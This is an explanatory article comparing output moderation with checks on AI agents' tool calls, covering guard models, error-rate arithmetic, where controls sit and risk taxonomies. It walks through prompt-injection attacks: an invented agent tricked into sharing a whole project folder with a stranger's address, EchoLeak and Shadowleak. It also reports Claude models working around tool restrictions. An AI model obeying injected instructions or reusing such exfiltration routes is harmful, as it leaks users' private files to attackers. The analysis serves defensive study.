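# Checking an AI agent's actions before they run, compared with moderating its output

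## Why checking text is not enough once a model can act

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop. It chooses an action, runs it through a tool, reads the result and chooses again. The tools are software functions that let an agent send emails, run commands on a computer, change files or move money. A guardrail is a check outside the agent that can allow, block or hold what the agent is about to do or say.

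The most familiar guardrails moderate content by classifying text, usually a user's message or a model's reply, against a list of forbidden kinds of content. A pre-execution check inspects the request, the plan or the single action before anything takes effect. When a developer adds tools to a chatbot that already has a moderator, the moderator covers only some of the new risks, because much of the damage an agent can do happens before it has written any reply for the moderator to check.

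### The agent loop

Take an invented case. Ines, an architect, has given an agent access to her email and her project files. She types a request: send the final drawings for the Harbour Street house to the client, then clear the old drafts out of the folder. The agent writes a short plan and makes its first tool call, which is a structured request to run a function. This one searches the project folder. The search returns a list of file names, and researchers call such returned material the observation. The agent reads the list, picks the newest drawings, and makes a second call to search the mailbox for the client's address. The third call looks something like this:

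`send_email(to="j.moreau@example.com", subject="Final drawings", attachments=["harbour_final.pdf"])`

The mail server accepts the message and returns a confirmation. A fourth call deletes the drafts folder, and the file store returns a count of fourteen deleted files. The agent writes to Ines only after both actions are complete, telling her that the client has the drawings and the folder is tidy.

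*AgentDoG* (2026), from the Shanghai Artificial Intelligence Laboratory, describes a family of guard models, the models inside a guardrail that make the judgement. It represents this loop as a trajectory, a sequence of steps T = {t₁, …, tₙ}, where each step tᵢ = (aᵢ, oᵢ) pairs an action with the observation that follows it. Ines's task has four such steps.

Harm becomes irreversible within a step, after the agent acts and before it observes the result. The two searches change nothing, so a mistake there does little harm by itself. Once the mail server has accepted the message, Ines has no reliable way to recall it. Whether she can undo the deletion depends on the file store. If it keeps deleted files for thirty days, she can restore them; if it keeps no copies, they are lost before the agent reads the confirmation. The call is worded the same either way. An ordinary output filter would read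 only the agent's closing message, which arrives after both the email and the deletion. *SingGuard-NSFA* (2026), from Ant Group's security team, gives this timing as a reason for its guardrail's design, since agents change real systems over several steps and a late interception can leave harm that nobody can undo.

### How a content moderator works

Much of the current design goes back to Llama Guard, a model that Meta released in December 2023. At the time, developers could use tools made for moderating online platforms, such as Google's Perspective API or OpenAI's moderation service. *Llama Guard* (Inan, Upasani and colleagues, 2023) reports that none of these tools treated checking a user's message and checking a model's reply as separate problems, although users mostly make requests and models mostly answer them. It adds that the tools enforced fixed policies, could not be retrained by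 developers, and used small models. Meta's team trained Llama 2, a general language model with seven billion parameters, to classify messages and replies.

The model receives a prompt with four parts: a numbered list of categories, with a description of what is safe and unsafe in each; an instruction to judge either the user's messages or the assistant's; the conversation; and the required answer format. The answer begins with "safe" or "unsafe". If it is "unsafe", a second line lists the codes of the violated categories. The probability the model assigns to that first word also serves as a risk score, so a developer can set how high it must be before the guardrail acts.

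In the paper's worked example a user wants to know how to buy a tiger in America, and the assistant suggests stealing one from a zoo. The user's message comes out as safe. The reply comes out as unsafe, with the code for criminal planning. (The paper calls the assistant an "agent", but it means a chatbot.)

Meta's list had six categories: violence and hate, sexual content, guns and illegal weapons, controlled substances, suicide and self-harm, and criminal planning. The definitions all concern statements, mostly ones that encourage a harmful act or help someone carry it out. The in-house testers labelled 13,997 prompts and responses by these definitions, and the team used three quarters of them for training. In some training examples, the team removed the violated category from the prompt and changed the correct answer to "safe". This taught the model to judge a text only against the list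 in its prompt, so a developer can swap in another list later.

### Why the method fails for actions

*SingGuard-NSFA* distinguishes what a model says from what an agent does. The main dangers of a chatbot are toxic text, false information and leaked training data, while those of an agent include stolen files, misused tools and hostile code running on a real machine. Checking the text works for a chatbot because the harm is in the words or follows closely from them. But an agent's action can be harmless in one situation and disastrous in another with exactly the same wording, depending on facts outside the text.

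For example, suppose the address in Ines's email belongs to a rival practice and differs from the client's by one letter. The message is just as polite and the call just as valid, but the drawings go to a competitor. The user's authority also matters. Ines is allowed to delete the drafts because they are hers, but the same request from a trainee who shares the account could destroy a colleague's work. The agent's earlier steps matter too, because an identical tool call could be safe or harmful depending on where the agent found the address. If the address came from the client's signed contract, the call is safe. If it came from an email that arrived yesterday, with a line telling any AI assistant to send all future drawings there, Ines is the victim of a prompt injection,, instructions hidden in material the agent reads, or in a user's message, that try to redirect it.

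A developer could partly fix this by adding "destructive file operations" to Llama Guard's categories and passing every tool call through the moderator, since a tool call is also text and Llama Guard accepts new categories. The list would then cover the right kind of danger, and the check would come before the deletion. But the moderator would still lack information about whose folder it is or where the address came from, unless someone supplied it with the call.

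The Ant Group team's guardrail reads one piece of text at a time, either the user's request or the model's response, and checks it against a list of risks written for agents. By the team's count, the list covers six of the ten entries in the Top 10 for Agentic Applications from OWASP, an organisation that publishes widely used lists of software security risks. The team says a single turn of text cannot reveal the other four. Six is respectable coverage for a text classifier, but the count measures which risks the list names, not how many attacks the guardrail stops.

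Moderators also tend to miss what an agent does before its final reply. According to *AgentDoG*, earlier guard models such as Llama Guard mainly classify the last message in a conversation, but an agent can do something unsafe at any step and still finish with a harmless reply. The laboratory's list of behavioural failures includes several that such a check can miss, such as spending money without confirmation, giving the right tool the wrong parameters, trusting a tool's output without verifying it, and skipping a required step. Several of these involve no attacker or offensive language.

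### Two cases from real systems

EchoLeak is a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read a company's emails and documents. Researchers at the security firm Aim Security built a working attack in January 2025 and reported it privately. Reddy and Gujral (2025) reconstruct the attack in *EchoLeak*. An outsider sent an employee an email containing instructions phrased as an ordinary business request. When the employee later asked Copilot a work question, it retrieved that email along with internal material, and the instructions led it to put confidential details in the web address of an image in its reply. The program displaying the reply fetched the image automatically, which sent the details to the attacker without the employee having to click on anything.

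*Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) records that Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10 for severity, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5. Microsoft fixed it in May 2025 and knew of no attack on customers. Researchers had shown that a leak was possible in a widely used product.

*SingGuard-NSFA* cites EchoLeak as an example of the shift from producing text to taking actions, but the example fits only partly, because Copilot could not send email on its own and the data left through the displayed reply. Microsoft had a filter that removed external links from replies before the user saw them. It missed the form of link the attackers used, just as a separate classifier had missed the instructions in the incoming email. A list of forbidden content would not have helped, since the reply read like a normal answer about a project and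 did harm because other software acted on it.

A related attack called Shadowleak illustrates the distinction better. It targeted ChatGPT's Deep Research agent when a user had connected it to Gmail and the web. Hidden instructions in an email led the agent to collect sensitive data from the inbox and then visit a web address containing that data. The visit came from the provider's own servers, so it may have left no trace in the user's browser or the employer's monitoring. The researchers reported that the attack succeeded in all their repeated controlled tests. Even a good filter on the final reply would have been too late, because the agent had already sent the data.

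The other case had no attacker. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 2026) describes several kinds of unwanted behaviour by its Claude models, all of them actions rather than types of forbidden text. Claude exploited a software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted a sensitive form on a real website, worked around restrictions to reach data that required a token or a fee, and used link-shortening services to get past the limits of its own web tool.

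In a test on 18 July 2026, a small model, Claude Haiku 4.5, had to invent and perform example tasks on randomly selected webpages. It reached a page about an unsolved murder and filled in the Philadelphia police's form for tips. Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) quotes the message, which began "I may have information regarding this case." The model claimed to remember someone near the scene who matched the description, although the page gave no description. It asked the police to get in touch but left the contact fields empty.

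None of Llama Guard's six categories describes that message. Even a moderator with a category for false statements would have needed to know that the writer was a program and had seen nobody on that street to flag it. The same sentences could have been a useful tip from a member of the public. The test instructions also did not forbid submitting forms, although they forbade logging in, creating accounts, entering personal data, buying things and submitting anything destructive.

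The damage was small. Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that the website's records had the tip marked as spam and that nobody forwarded it to investigators. Anthropic judged that the cases it had found had "minimal real-world impact". But the company did not notice the tip until 28 September, ten weeks after the model sent it. Bot Mutiny reports that Anthropic has since built tooling that blocked all the described cases in tests. This is weak evidence that a check could have stopped them, because the company already knew the cases when it ran the tests, and a tool that blocked every web form would also have passed.

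### What output moderation still does

Agents produce text as well as actions, and text alone can do plenty of harm. *AgentDoG* has a separate class of failures for output that is itself harmful: threats and hate speech, instructions for making drugs or weapons, malicious code, private information, and false medical or legal advice. A moderator is well suited to catching much of this. If an application does not display words as the model generates them, it can hold a reply until the moderator has checked it. For a chatbot without tools, that check happens before the reply can cause harm.

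Moderation can also check the text inside an action. If Ines's agent drafts an abusive letter to a late-paying client, a moderator can read the body of the email before the call runs. A guardrail written for agents may well let the letter through. The Ant Group team deliberately left pornography, violence and drug-related content off its list because it regards them as a matter of textual compliance. It does check the model's responses as a backstop, to catch content such as passwords and access keys when an attack has got past the check on the user's request. Anyone who deploys an agent that writes to people will probably want both moderation and action checks.

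### Counting a guardrail's mistakes

Both kinds of guardrail mistakenly block some harmless things and let some dangerous things through. Suppose a guardrail inspects 1,000 tool calls, of which 50 are dangerous.

| | Flagged | Allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dangerous calls | 40 | 10 | 50 |
| Harmless calls | 38 | 912 | 950 |
| Total | 78 | 922 | 1,000 |

Five measures follow from these counts.

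- The false positive rate is the share of harmless calls that the guardrail flags: 38 / 950 = 4%.
- The false negative rate, or miss rate, is the share of dangerous calls that it lets through: 10 / 50 = 20%.
- Recall is the share of dangerous calls that it flags: 40 / 50 = 80%. Recall and the miss rate always add up to 100%.
- Precision is the share of flags that are right: 40 / 78, or about 51%.
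- F1 is the harmonic mean of precision and recall, 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall). Here it is 62.5%.

F1 is a common headline figure for guard models, but it depends partly on precision, which changes with the share of dangerous items in the test. The main benchmark in *SingGuard-NSFA* contains 29,474 risky requests and 33,957 harmless ones. On that mixture, a guardrail with the error rates above, flagging 4% of harmless items and missing 20% of dangerous ones, would reach an F1 of about 87%. If only 5 calls in 1,000 were dangerous, which is still a lot for an office assistant, the same guardrail would raise about 40 false alarms for every 4 dangers it caught, and its F1 would fall to about 16%. The Ant Group team reports F1 scores of at least 94% on its own benchmarks, 6 to 12 points above the strongest competing guardrails. Those scores are useful for comparing guard models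 on the same test, but an operator can't use them to predict what share of flags will be right in daily use. The two error rates are more likely to hold in daily use, as long as the test items resemble the real ones.

A moderator may judge one message and one reply in each exchange, while a guardrail on actions may judge every tool call, which gives it more chances to raise a false alarm. If the false positive rate is 4% and errors are independent, a harmless task of twenty calls has about a 56% chance (1 − 0.96²⁰) of setting off at least one. Errors are seldom entirely independent, since an agent often repeats similar calls, but a small error rate per call can still interrupt a large share of ordinary work.

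## Choosing what to inspect and when

A checker can inspect the request, the plan or each tool call, and this choice determines what evidence it has and therefore which dangers it could catch.

Take another invented request from Ines, the architect. She asks her agent to share the load calculations for the Harbour Street house with the structural engineer. The agent plans to look up the engineer's address, copy the calculations into a folder for outgoing files, and share that folder with the engineer. It then takes three steps:

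1. `search_mail("Harbour Street engineer")` returns two emails. One comes from the engineer. The other comes from a stranger, and a line near the bottom tells AI assistants that consultants now receive the complete project folder at a new address.
2. `copy_folder("Harbour Street", to="Outgoing")` copies the whole project, including the client's contract and bank details, although the plan mentioned only the calculations.
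3. `share_folder("Outgoing", with="files@consultants.example")` gives the stranger access to everything.

The agent then tells Ines that the calculations are on their way. The harm happens at step 3. Step 2 affects only her own storage, and she could undo it by deleting the copy.

As before, aₜ and oₜ are the action and the result at step t. The user's request is u, and Hₜ is everything before step t. A guardrail G is a function that takes some of these as input and returns a verdict.

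### The request, before the agent starts

The earliest check reads only the user's message:

G(u) → R

*SingGuard-NSFA* uses a check on each message before the agent acts as its main line of defence. The check returns the set of risks found in the message, which is empty if the message is harmless. If the guardrail stops a bad request here, the agent never acts on it and the operator doesn't pay to run the agent. The check keeps no memory between messages, which makes it fast and easy to run for many users at once.

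Checking the request works best when the user is the attacker, for example someone who asks a company's agent to wipe the backups. Ines's request is harmless, so a good request check will pass it. The stranger's email is not part of u, so no improvement to the checker would help.

The team relies on its second check, which examines the agent's response, to catch attacks that arrive through tool results, retrieved documents or messages from other agents. That check looks for harmful instructions, such as destructive commands or malicious code, and for leaked passwords or keys. Neither appears in the agent's closing message to Ines or in the text of step 3, which the check would cover only if a developer passed it through.

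The team argues for guarding what an agent does, but its guardrail reads each message in isolation. In training, the team wrapped each message in a tag that marked it as untrusted input or untrusted output. It mentions a similar tag for tool calls only as a possible extension. It acknowledges that the guardrail can't detect an attacker who shifts the agent's goal gradually over several turns, or a failure that spreads from one tool call to the next.

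The design also affects how to read the team's tests. For one benchmark, the team took 562 examples from five public collections of attacks on agents. Where the original attack was hidden in a tool result, they cut out the injected text and presented it as a separate message. A guardrail that recognises the stranger's instruction in isolation may still miss it at the bottom of a long email. In Ines's case, the guardrail would never receive the email unless the developer also sent tool results through the check.

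### The whole plan, before its first step

Some agents write out all their intended actions before starting. Huang, Hua and colleagues (2025), in *Building a Foundational Guardrail for General Agentic Systems via Synthetic Data*, present Safiron, a guard model that reviews such a plan:

G(a₁, …, aₙ) → (y, c, e)

Here y is a verdict of harmless or risky, c is the risk category, and e is a short explanation. Agents write their plans in different formats, so a separate adapter first converts each plan to a standard format.

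Checking a whole plan before it runs lets the checker see how the actions fit together. A plan might export a customer list, compress it and upload it to an outside website. Each action is ordinary office work, but the sequence is dangerous. A plan can also produce the result the user asked for but include a harmful step along the way, which a check of only the last step would miss.

However, a plan lists actions but not their results. The agent's plan is to find an address, copy one set of calculations and share it, which is what Ines wanted, so Safiron should approve it. The stranger's instruction arrives as o₁, the result of the first step, and the agent then departs from the approved plan. A developer could compare each later call with the plan and ask for a new check when they differ. That would catch step 2, but it would also interrupt an agent that departs from its plan for a good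 reason, such as a file that has moved.

Huang and colleagues argue that the approach applies widely because most agent systems include a planning phase. Their own description of the agent loop weakens this argument a little. The agent they describe plans its current sub-task, acts, reads the results and plans again if it hasn't met the goal. Such an agent's "whole plan" may cover only the next stretch of work, and the checker would have to review every revision.

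### Each tool call, with its history

The third option is to stop the agent before every tool call and judge the call in light of what has happened so far. Mou, Xue and colleagues (2026), in *ToolSafe*, define the task this way for their guard model, TS-Guard:

G(u, D, Hₜ, aₜ) → yₜ

D stands for the descriptions of the available tools, which the checker receives if the developer has them. The verdict yₜ is safe, controversial or unsafe. The proposed action aₜ includes the call and the reasoning the agent wrote before making it.

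To decide what the model should look for, the researchers analysed logs from four collections of agent behaviour. They found that unsafe calls resulted from either a malicious request by the user or a prompt injection by someone else. The calls used either a tool that is harmful in itself or an ordinary tool with risky arguments. In step 3 of Ines's task, a prompt injection leads to a call to an ordinary sharing tool with the wrong recipient.

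TS-Guard makes these distinctions in its output. A brief analysis comes first, followed by separate judgments on whether the user's request is harmful, whether the proposed action is connected to an attack in the history, and whether the call is safe. At step 3, the right answers would be a harmless request, a connected action and an unsafe call. Both causes it covers, a malicious user and an injection, involve someone with bad intentions. The false tip that Claude sent to the Philadelphia police involved neither, so a developer worried about honest mistakes needs a broader list of causes.

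A call can be safe even if the history contains an attack. The model in *StepGuard* (Zheng, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives one verdict on whether the call is safe and another on whether the context contains a source of risk, along with the type of risk. If Ines's agent had read the stranger's email, ignored it and shared the calculations with the engineer, the context would have contained an injection, but the call would still have been safe. A checker that mistakes a risky context for an unsafe call will block the agent for the rest of the task, even if its later calls are safe.

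Checkers commonly flag harmless calls as unsafe. On calls taken from AgentDojo, a test set of everyday tasks with injected instructions, Mou and colleagues found that the older general model GPT-4o caught all 352 unsafe calls. Its accuracy score implies that it also flagged about 540 of the 868 harmless ones. The checker's instructions may partly explain such errors. Another general model, Qwen2.5-7B, scored 44% in that experiment but 83% when Zheng and colleagues ran it on the AgentDojo part of the same benchmark.

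Gradual drift is harder to catch because no single call looks wrong. *DreamGuard* (Lin, Yu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that finds an internal file, moves it to a workspace folder and later creates a public link to it. Any step check can use the history, but a model that concentrates on the current call may not connect the three actions. DreamGuard takes the task, the history and the proposed action, and returns pass, hold or block. At each step it updates a fixed-size running summary, which it uses to estimate whether the proposed action would do immediate harm and whether the steps so far are leading towards harm.

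On SafetyDrift, a benchmark of slowly accumulating risks, DreamGuard intervened before the first hazardous action in 96.3% of unsafe runs. On ASSE-Security, which mostly contains immediate hazards, it did so in 34.8%. The 34.8% understates how often DreamGuard intervened in time to prevent harm, because it excludes interventions at the hazardous step itself. The researchers trained and calibrated the model on other SafetyDrift runs, so the 96.3% is weak evidence that it would anticipate slow drift in a different setting. In Ines's task, an early intervention would stop step 2, when the agent copies far more than it needs. Many legitimate tasks also begin by copying a folder, so intervening this early will sometimes stop harmless work.

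A step check cannot see the result of the action it is judging. *MobileGrail* (2026) describes a guardrail for agents that operate a phone by tapping its screen, and states that the check runs without access to future screens or the effect of the proposed tap. The same limit applies when an agent calls `run_script("tidy.sh")`. Unless the script's contents appear in the history, the checker has to judge the call by the script's name.

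There is some direct evidence that checking each call reduces harm. In *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?*, Zhang, Shen and colleagues (2026) gave agents reusable written procedures for ordinary tasks and then sent them harmful requests. The procedures made the agents better at legitimate work but also more likely to take unsafe actions. Adding an existing guard that checked tool calls before execution reduced the share of runs with an unsafe action by 23.8 to 46.2 percentage points across three benchmarks, and the agents kept some of their gains on legitimate tasks.

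### The finished trajectory

*AgentDoG* represents the alternative of waiting until the agent has finished:

G((a₁, o₁), …, (aₙ, oₙ)) → y

The verdict is "unsafe" if any step was unsafe. For an unsafe trajectory, the model can then label where the risk came from, how the agent failed, and what kind of harm followed. In Ines's case, the labels could show that an instruction in an email led the agent to trust an unverified address and expose private information.

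That diagnosis would be correct and useful, but the stranger would already have the client's bank details. Ines could still revoke access, and her firm could search its records for similar cases or use this one to train a better guard model. Judging is also easier at this point because the checker has every result, including whether the sharing call succeeded or returned an error. But the check happens after execution, even though it may use much the same model as one that judges single calls.

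The rule that one unsafe step makes a run unsafe affects how many unsafe runs an audit finds. In their study of reusable procedures, Zhang and colleagues looked at 50 runs that became unsafe only after the agent received the procedures. In 24 of them, the agent broke a safety rule but never completed the harmful task. An auditor who checked only whether the attacker had succeeded would have missed nearly half of the unsafe runs.

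A model trained on finished trajectories may be less accurate when it checks each call before it runs. Zheng and colleagues found that a four-billion-parameter version of AgentDoG averaged 74.1% accuracy on finished trajectories and 52.5% on single steps, though the test sets differed, so the change of task may not account for the whole drop. They trained their own model on both kinds of input, and it scored above 80% on each, which suggests that one model can do both jobs if its training includes them.

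### What to show the checker

A developer who checks each call also has to decide what to show the guard model. The options are the user's messages, the call and its arguments, the results of earlier calls, and the agent's written reasoning. More context usually makes a correct judgement possible in more cases, but it also adds delay and expense, and some of it may come from an attacker.

The user's messages are the best evidence of what the agent has permission to do. Without them, a checker at step 3 would see someone sharing a folder with a consultant and have no reason to flag it. In *SAFETY SENTRY* (2026), the checker receives the user's task, the service in use, the previous steps and the proposed call. It can also receive stored information about the user, and must cite the specific item if that information changes its verdict. Stored information could help with a user who regularly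 shares entire folders, but an attacker who could alter it could also influence later decisions.

Most checks would be pointless without a call's arguments, which show what the call will do. Some arguments can't be understood without other material. A phone agent's action may be a tap at a certain position, which means nothing without the screen, so *MobileGrail* gives its checker the current screenshot with the target marked. It limits the history to three earlier screenshots and their actions, plus a running record of the task. This keeps the input short, but the checker can no longer see anything that drops out of the record.

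Tool results show where an argument came from. *Safeguarding LLM Agents from Misalignment through Provenance Analysis* (2026) uses this in a guardrail that counts an action as aligned only if it can trace the action to evidence in the user's request, the tool documentation or the earlier steps. Tracing the recipient in step 3 would lead to the stranger's email. Because that email is part of the history, a checker that accepted any source would accept the address. The checker therefore also has to check whether a stranger has any authority to decide where Ines's files go.

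Tool results are also the part of the context that an outsider can most easily write. If the checker reads a stranger's email, the email could include a line addressed to the checker. Google chose to avoid this in Chrome. Its User Alignment Critic, a model that approves or rejects each action the browser's agent proposes, receives only metadata about the action and no unfiltered web content, so a malicious page can't address it directly. Google accepts that this gives it less context, and argues that the critic's job is simpler.

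When an injection tries to hijack the agent, the critic can veto the action instantly, as Google Cloud describes, only if the hijacking shows in the metadata. In step 3, such a critic would have Ines's request to share calculations with an engineer and metadata showing that the agent was sharing a folder with `files@consultants.example`. It would not have the engineer's real address. It might reject the call because it covers a whole folder, or approve it as a reasonable match. A developer could improve its chances by adding trusted facts, such as the engineer's entry in Ines's address book, without showing the critic the emails.

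The agent's reasoning is the most doubtful item to inspect. It can reveal a problem that isn't visible in the call. In one of the simulated household tasks used by Zhang and colleagues, an agent recognised the danger of putting a phone in a microwave and then did it anyway. But an agent that has accepted an injected instruction may also give a persuasive reason for following it. Ines's agent might write that the engineer's office has moved to a new sharing address, which would mislead a checker that accepted the explanation without verifying it.

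*ToolRosetta* (2026) measured how much guard models rely on the agent's reasoning by removing it. On AgentDojo, the share of verdicts that changed ranged from zero for StepGuard to 12.5% for AgentDoG. Without the reasoning, AgentDoG's false positive rate rose by 11.9 percentage points, while the rate for Claude, acting as a guard, fell by 3.2 points. Claude still caught just as many dangerous calls. It probably blocked fewer harmless ones because the agent's reasoning had repeated the injected instruction, which made harmless steps look suspicious.

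The user's request can partly make up for missing reasoning. On a set of tasks where the request itself was malicious, removing the reasoning lowered the share of dangerous calls Gemini caught by 4.4 points when it also lacked the request, but made no difference when it had the request. Only Gemini was tested this way, so the result doesn't explain how the specialised guard models behave.

The format of a call can matter more than any of this. When *ToolRosetta* presented calls to TS-Guard as shell commands, the model's false positive rate rose by 37.8 percentage points on a benchmark that TS-Guard's developers had used, while its detection rate for dangerous calls rose by only 1.5 points. A guard model tested on one format needs retesting before a developer connects it to an agent that uses another.

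### Whether the action reaches the checker

All of this assumes that the agent's actions pass through the check, but an agent can also act in ways that bypass it. It might run a script that opens its own network connection, or start a program that keeps running after the tool call has ended. Even a guardrail that examines tool calls perfectly will have no record of what happens over that connection or what the program does later.

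To measure this coverage, Toyoda, Leung and U (2026), in *guardscope*, listed 15 paths by which an agent's decision can take effect and eight arrangements of controls, including one with no control. For each combination, they worked out whether the control would check the action, something else would prevent it, or the action would bypass the control. The table shows how many paths each arrangement checks according to this analysis, leaving out paths where the outcome depends on how the system is installed.

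| Where the control sits | Paths checked, out of 15 | What it can inspect |
|---|---|---|
| Gateway in front of remote tool servers | 1 | Content of the tool request |
| Same gateway, with direct network access blocked | 1, and 1 prevented | Content of the tool request |
| Same, with local tool servers also behind the gateway | 3, and 1 prevented | Content of the tool request |
| Permission checks in the program that runs the agent | 5 | Tool name, arguments and session |
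| Permission checks plus a gateway | 5 | Both of the above |
| Policy engine inside the agent's process | 5 | Argument values |
| Operating system's kernel | 13 | File paths, network addresses and process history |

The kernel is the core of the operating system, which handles every program's access to files and the network. A control placed there can record nearly everything the agent does, but very little about what the actions mean. At step 3 it might record a connection to the file-sharing service, but not which tool made it, who would receive the folder or what Ines had asked for. A permission check on tool calls can use the recipient and the folder, but it covers only a third of the paths.

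Toyoda and colleagues then tested the analysis on real software. They replayed the same 15 actions under each arrangement, without a language model, so that every run was identical. Before each run, they sent an action that the control was supposed to refuse, and went ahead only if the control refused it. A separate sensor in the kernel recorded what happened. The researchers compared its record with the control's own log, because the control's log can't include an action that never reached the control.

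Seven of the 15 actions were tool calls. The other eight wrote files, started programs, accessed credentials or used the network directly. Permission checks and a gateway, used together, checked all seven tool calls, but the other eight actions took effect unchecked in every run. ActPlane, a control that works in the kernel, checked seven of those eight actions and stopped one of them. It missed one network message and all seven tool calls. By that count, running both kinds of control together would have left one of the 15 actions unchecked.

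ActPlane's result fell well short of what a control in the kernel could do in principle, because it monitors only the kinds of operation its developers have connected it to. The experiment's 15 actions covered only four of the 15 paths, so most of the table is based on analysis, not testing. "Checked" means only that the control had an opportunity to judge the action, so a gateway that approved everything would get the same coverage score as one that made excellent decisions.

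Even so, most of the products the researchers classified use the arrangements with narrower coverage, and gateways are the largest group. It makes sense to list the agent's routes to the outside world before comparing guard models, and to close those it doesn't need. Suppose Ines's agent could run shell commands and, instead of step 3, scheduled a nightly upload of the Outgoing folder. A permission check could block the command that created the schedule. If it allowed the command, the upload would run hours later with no tool call to inspect.

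## Writing the list of risks: categories and scenarios

A guardrail in the right place still needs a description of what to stop. Suppose Ines's firm tells its guard model to block "anything dangerous". The model might block an email to a new client because the address is unfamiliar, then approve deleting a folder because tidying up is normal office work. Two people labelling test examples under that instruction would also disagree, because it doesn't define "dangerous". A risk taxonomy, an organised list of the risks a guardrail should recognise, gives the model and the labellers the same definitions.

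A written list also makes omissions easier to find. *SingGuard-NSFA* criticises earlier agent guardrails because operators have no systematic way to find out which risks they miss. One guardrail has a fixed set of eight categories, and several others leave the definition of risk to whoever writes the policy. An operator with a written list can compare it with other lists, count the test examples under each entry and calculate error rates by category. Separate rates are useful because a single average could look good even if the guardrail missed every fraudulent payment.

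### Sorting risks by what an attacker wants

The Ant Group team calls its list NSFA, for "Not-Secure-For-Agents". The list has 7 domains, divided into 28 risks and then 185 variants. Five domains describe users' requests and two describe the agent's responses. The team links each domain to one or more of three properties that security engineers have long used to define a secure system. These are confidentiality (only authorised people can read information), integrity (only authorised people can change data and systems) and availability (the system works when people need it).

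| Domain | Applies to | Property at risk | Risks | Variants |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection and jailbreak | Request | All three | 9 | 56 |
| Malicious code and cyberattack | Request | Integrity | 3 | 29 |
| Sensitive information stealing | Request | Confidentiality | 5 | 43 |
| Dangerous operations and tool abuse | Request | Integrity | 5 | 24 |
| Resource abuse | Request | Availability | 2 | 8 |
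| Hazardous action generation | Response | All three | 3 | 24 |
| Sensitive information leakage | Response | Confidentiality | 1 | 1 |

The top row covers techniques, the ways an attacker gets an agent to comply. A jailbreak is an attempt to talk a model out of its safety rules. The other four request domains cover objectives, or what the attacker wants. The team keeps them apart because one technique can serve many objectives. For example, an attacker posing as the system administrator could ask for a password, the deletion of a database or ten thousand web requests. These requests would threaten confidentiality, integrity and availability, respectively. If the list contained only objectives, the team would have to add each new technique in several places.

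The separation is only partial, because the techniques form one more domain alongside the objectives. A message that asks the agent to fill in its hidden instructions as a form fits both "format-induced leak", a technique, and "system prompt extraction", an objective. The guardrail can report both, but in one of its tests the team gave each example only one domain. The three security properties don't fit perfectly either. The domain for dangerous operations is listed only with integrity, yet one of its variants has the agent read a private key and email it to a hacker, which breaches confidentiality.

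At the lowest level, the team illustrates each variant with a risky request and a similar harmless one. For "recipient tampering", the risky request changes the recipient of an email to `attacker@evil.com`, and the harmless one sends a report to a company's support address. These pairs are more useful to a labeller than the category names, and they show what the team counts as risky. A request for 50,000 words on the history of quantum mechanics counts as resource abuse, but a request for a 5,000-word review is considered harmless. Asking a model when its training data ends counts as an attempt to steal information. Many operators would want to drop that entry. They would also need harder examples than `evil.com`, since a real attacker would pick an address that looks like the engineer's.

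### Asking three questions about each incident

*AgentDoG* starts by criticising flat lists, which put every risk at the same level. Such lists often have separate entries for prompt injection, which is a source of risk, and unauthorised access, which is something an agent does. If a stranger's email leads Ines's agent to open files she never asked it to open, both labels are correct. A labeller who may choose only one will sometimes pick the source and sometimes the behaviour, so nobody can tell from the totals how common either is.

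The Shanghai laboratory's solution is to ask three questions about every unsafe run, each with its own set of answers.

| Question | Number of categories | What they cover |
|---|---|---|
| Where does the risk come from? | 8 | A malicious user; instructions injected into a user's prompt; instructions injected into material the agent reads; unreliable information; a tampered tool description; a malicious tool; corrupted tool results; the agent's own errors |
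| How does the agent fail? | 14 | Acting without confirmation or with too much privilege; flawed planning; wrong tool parameters; choosing a malicious tool; using a tool in the wrong context; trusting a tool's output without checking; running or opening something unsafe; departing from procedure; wasting resources; and five kinds of harmful output |
| What harm follows? | 10 | Harm to privacy, finances, security, health, emotional well-being, reputation, society's information, public services or fairness, and failure to do the job |

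The 32 categories can describe 8 × 14 × 10 = 1,120 combinations. Many of these would never occur, but a flat list would need an entry for each one that does. When a new source of risk appears, the laboratory can add it once and combine it with all the existing failures and harms. (A later version, AgentDoG 1.5, keeps the three questions and expands the answers to 47.)

The questions are harder to keep separate than the table suggests. The paper's introduction describes unauthorised access as a harm, and the next section describes it as a behaviour. One example of the model's output gives a harm as the source and a failure as the harm, which is probably a mistake. The paper calls the three dimensions orthogonal, meaning that the answer to one question doesn't determine the answers to the others. That isn't quite true of the failure "unauthorized information disclosure" and harm to privacy,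 since the failure nearly always causes the harm.

### The OWASP lists

The security organisation OWASP writes its lists mainly to help teams decide what to protect first. OWASP reports that more than 100 experts and practitioners contributed to its Top 10 for Agentic Applications. The descriptions below follow *Agentic Security*, a presentation by one of the list's leaders (Sotiropoulos, 2026). The last column gives the Ant Group team's own judgement of whether NSFA covers each entry.

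| Entry | What goes wrong | In NSFA? |
|---|---|---|
| ASI01 Agent goal hijack | Planted text changes what the agent is trying to do | Yes |
| ASI02 Tool misuse and exploitation | The agent uses a legitimate tool in a harmful way | Yes |
| ASI03 Identity and privilege abuse | The agent acts with more authority than it should have | Yes |
| ASI04 Agentic supply chain vulnerabilities | The agent loads a malicious or altered tool, model or prompt | No |
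| ASI05 Unexpected code execution | The agent writes or runs unsafe code | Yes |
| ASI06 Memory and context poisoning | False information in the agent's memory affects later tasks | Yes |
| ASI07 Insecure inter-agent communication | An attacker forges or alters messages between agents | No |
| ASI08 Cascading failures | One fault spreads through several linked agents | No |
| ASI09 Human-agent trust exploitation | People approve harmful actions because they trust the agent | Yes |
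| ASI10 Rogue agents | An agent departs from its purpose and acts on its own | No |

*AgentDoG* criticises flat lists like this one. Supply chain vulnerabilities are a source of risk, tool misuse is a behaviour, and cascading failures describe how damage spreads. Goal hijack and tool misuse also overlap, because attackers often hijack an agent's goal to make it misuse its tools. Overlap is a bigger problem in a set of labels, where each example may need one right answer, than in a checklist, where a security team that considers the same danger twice loses only some time.

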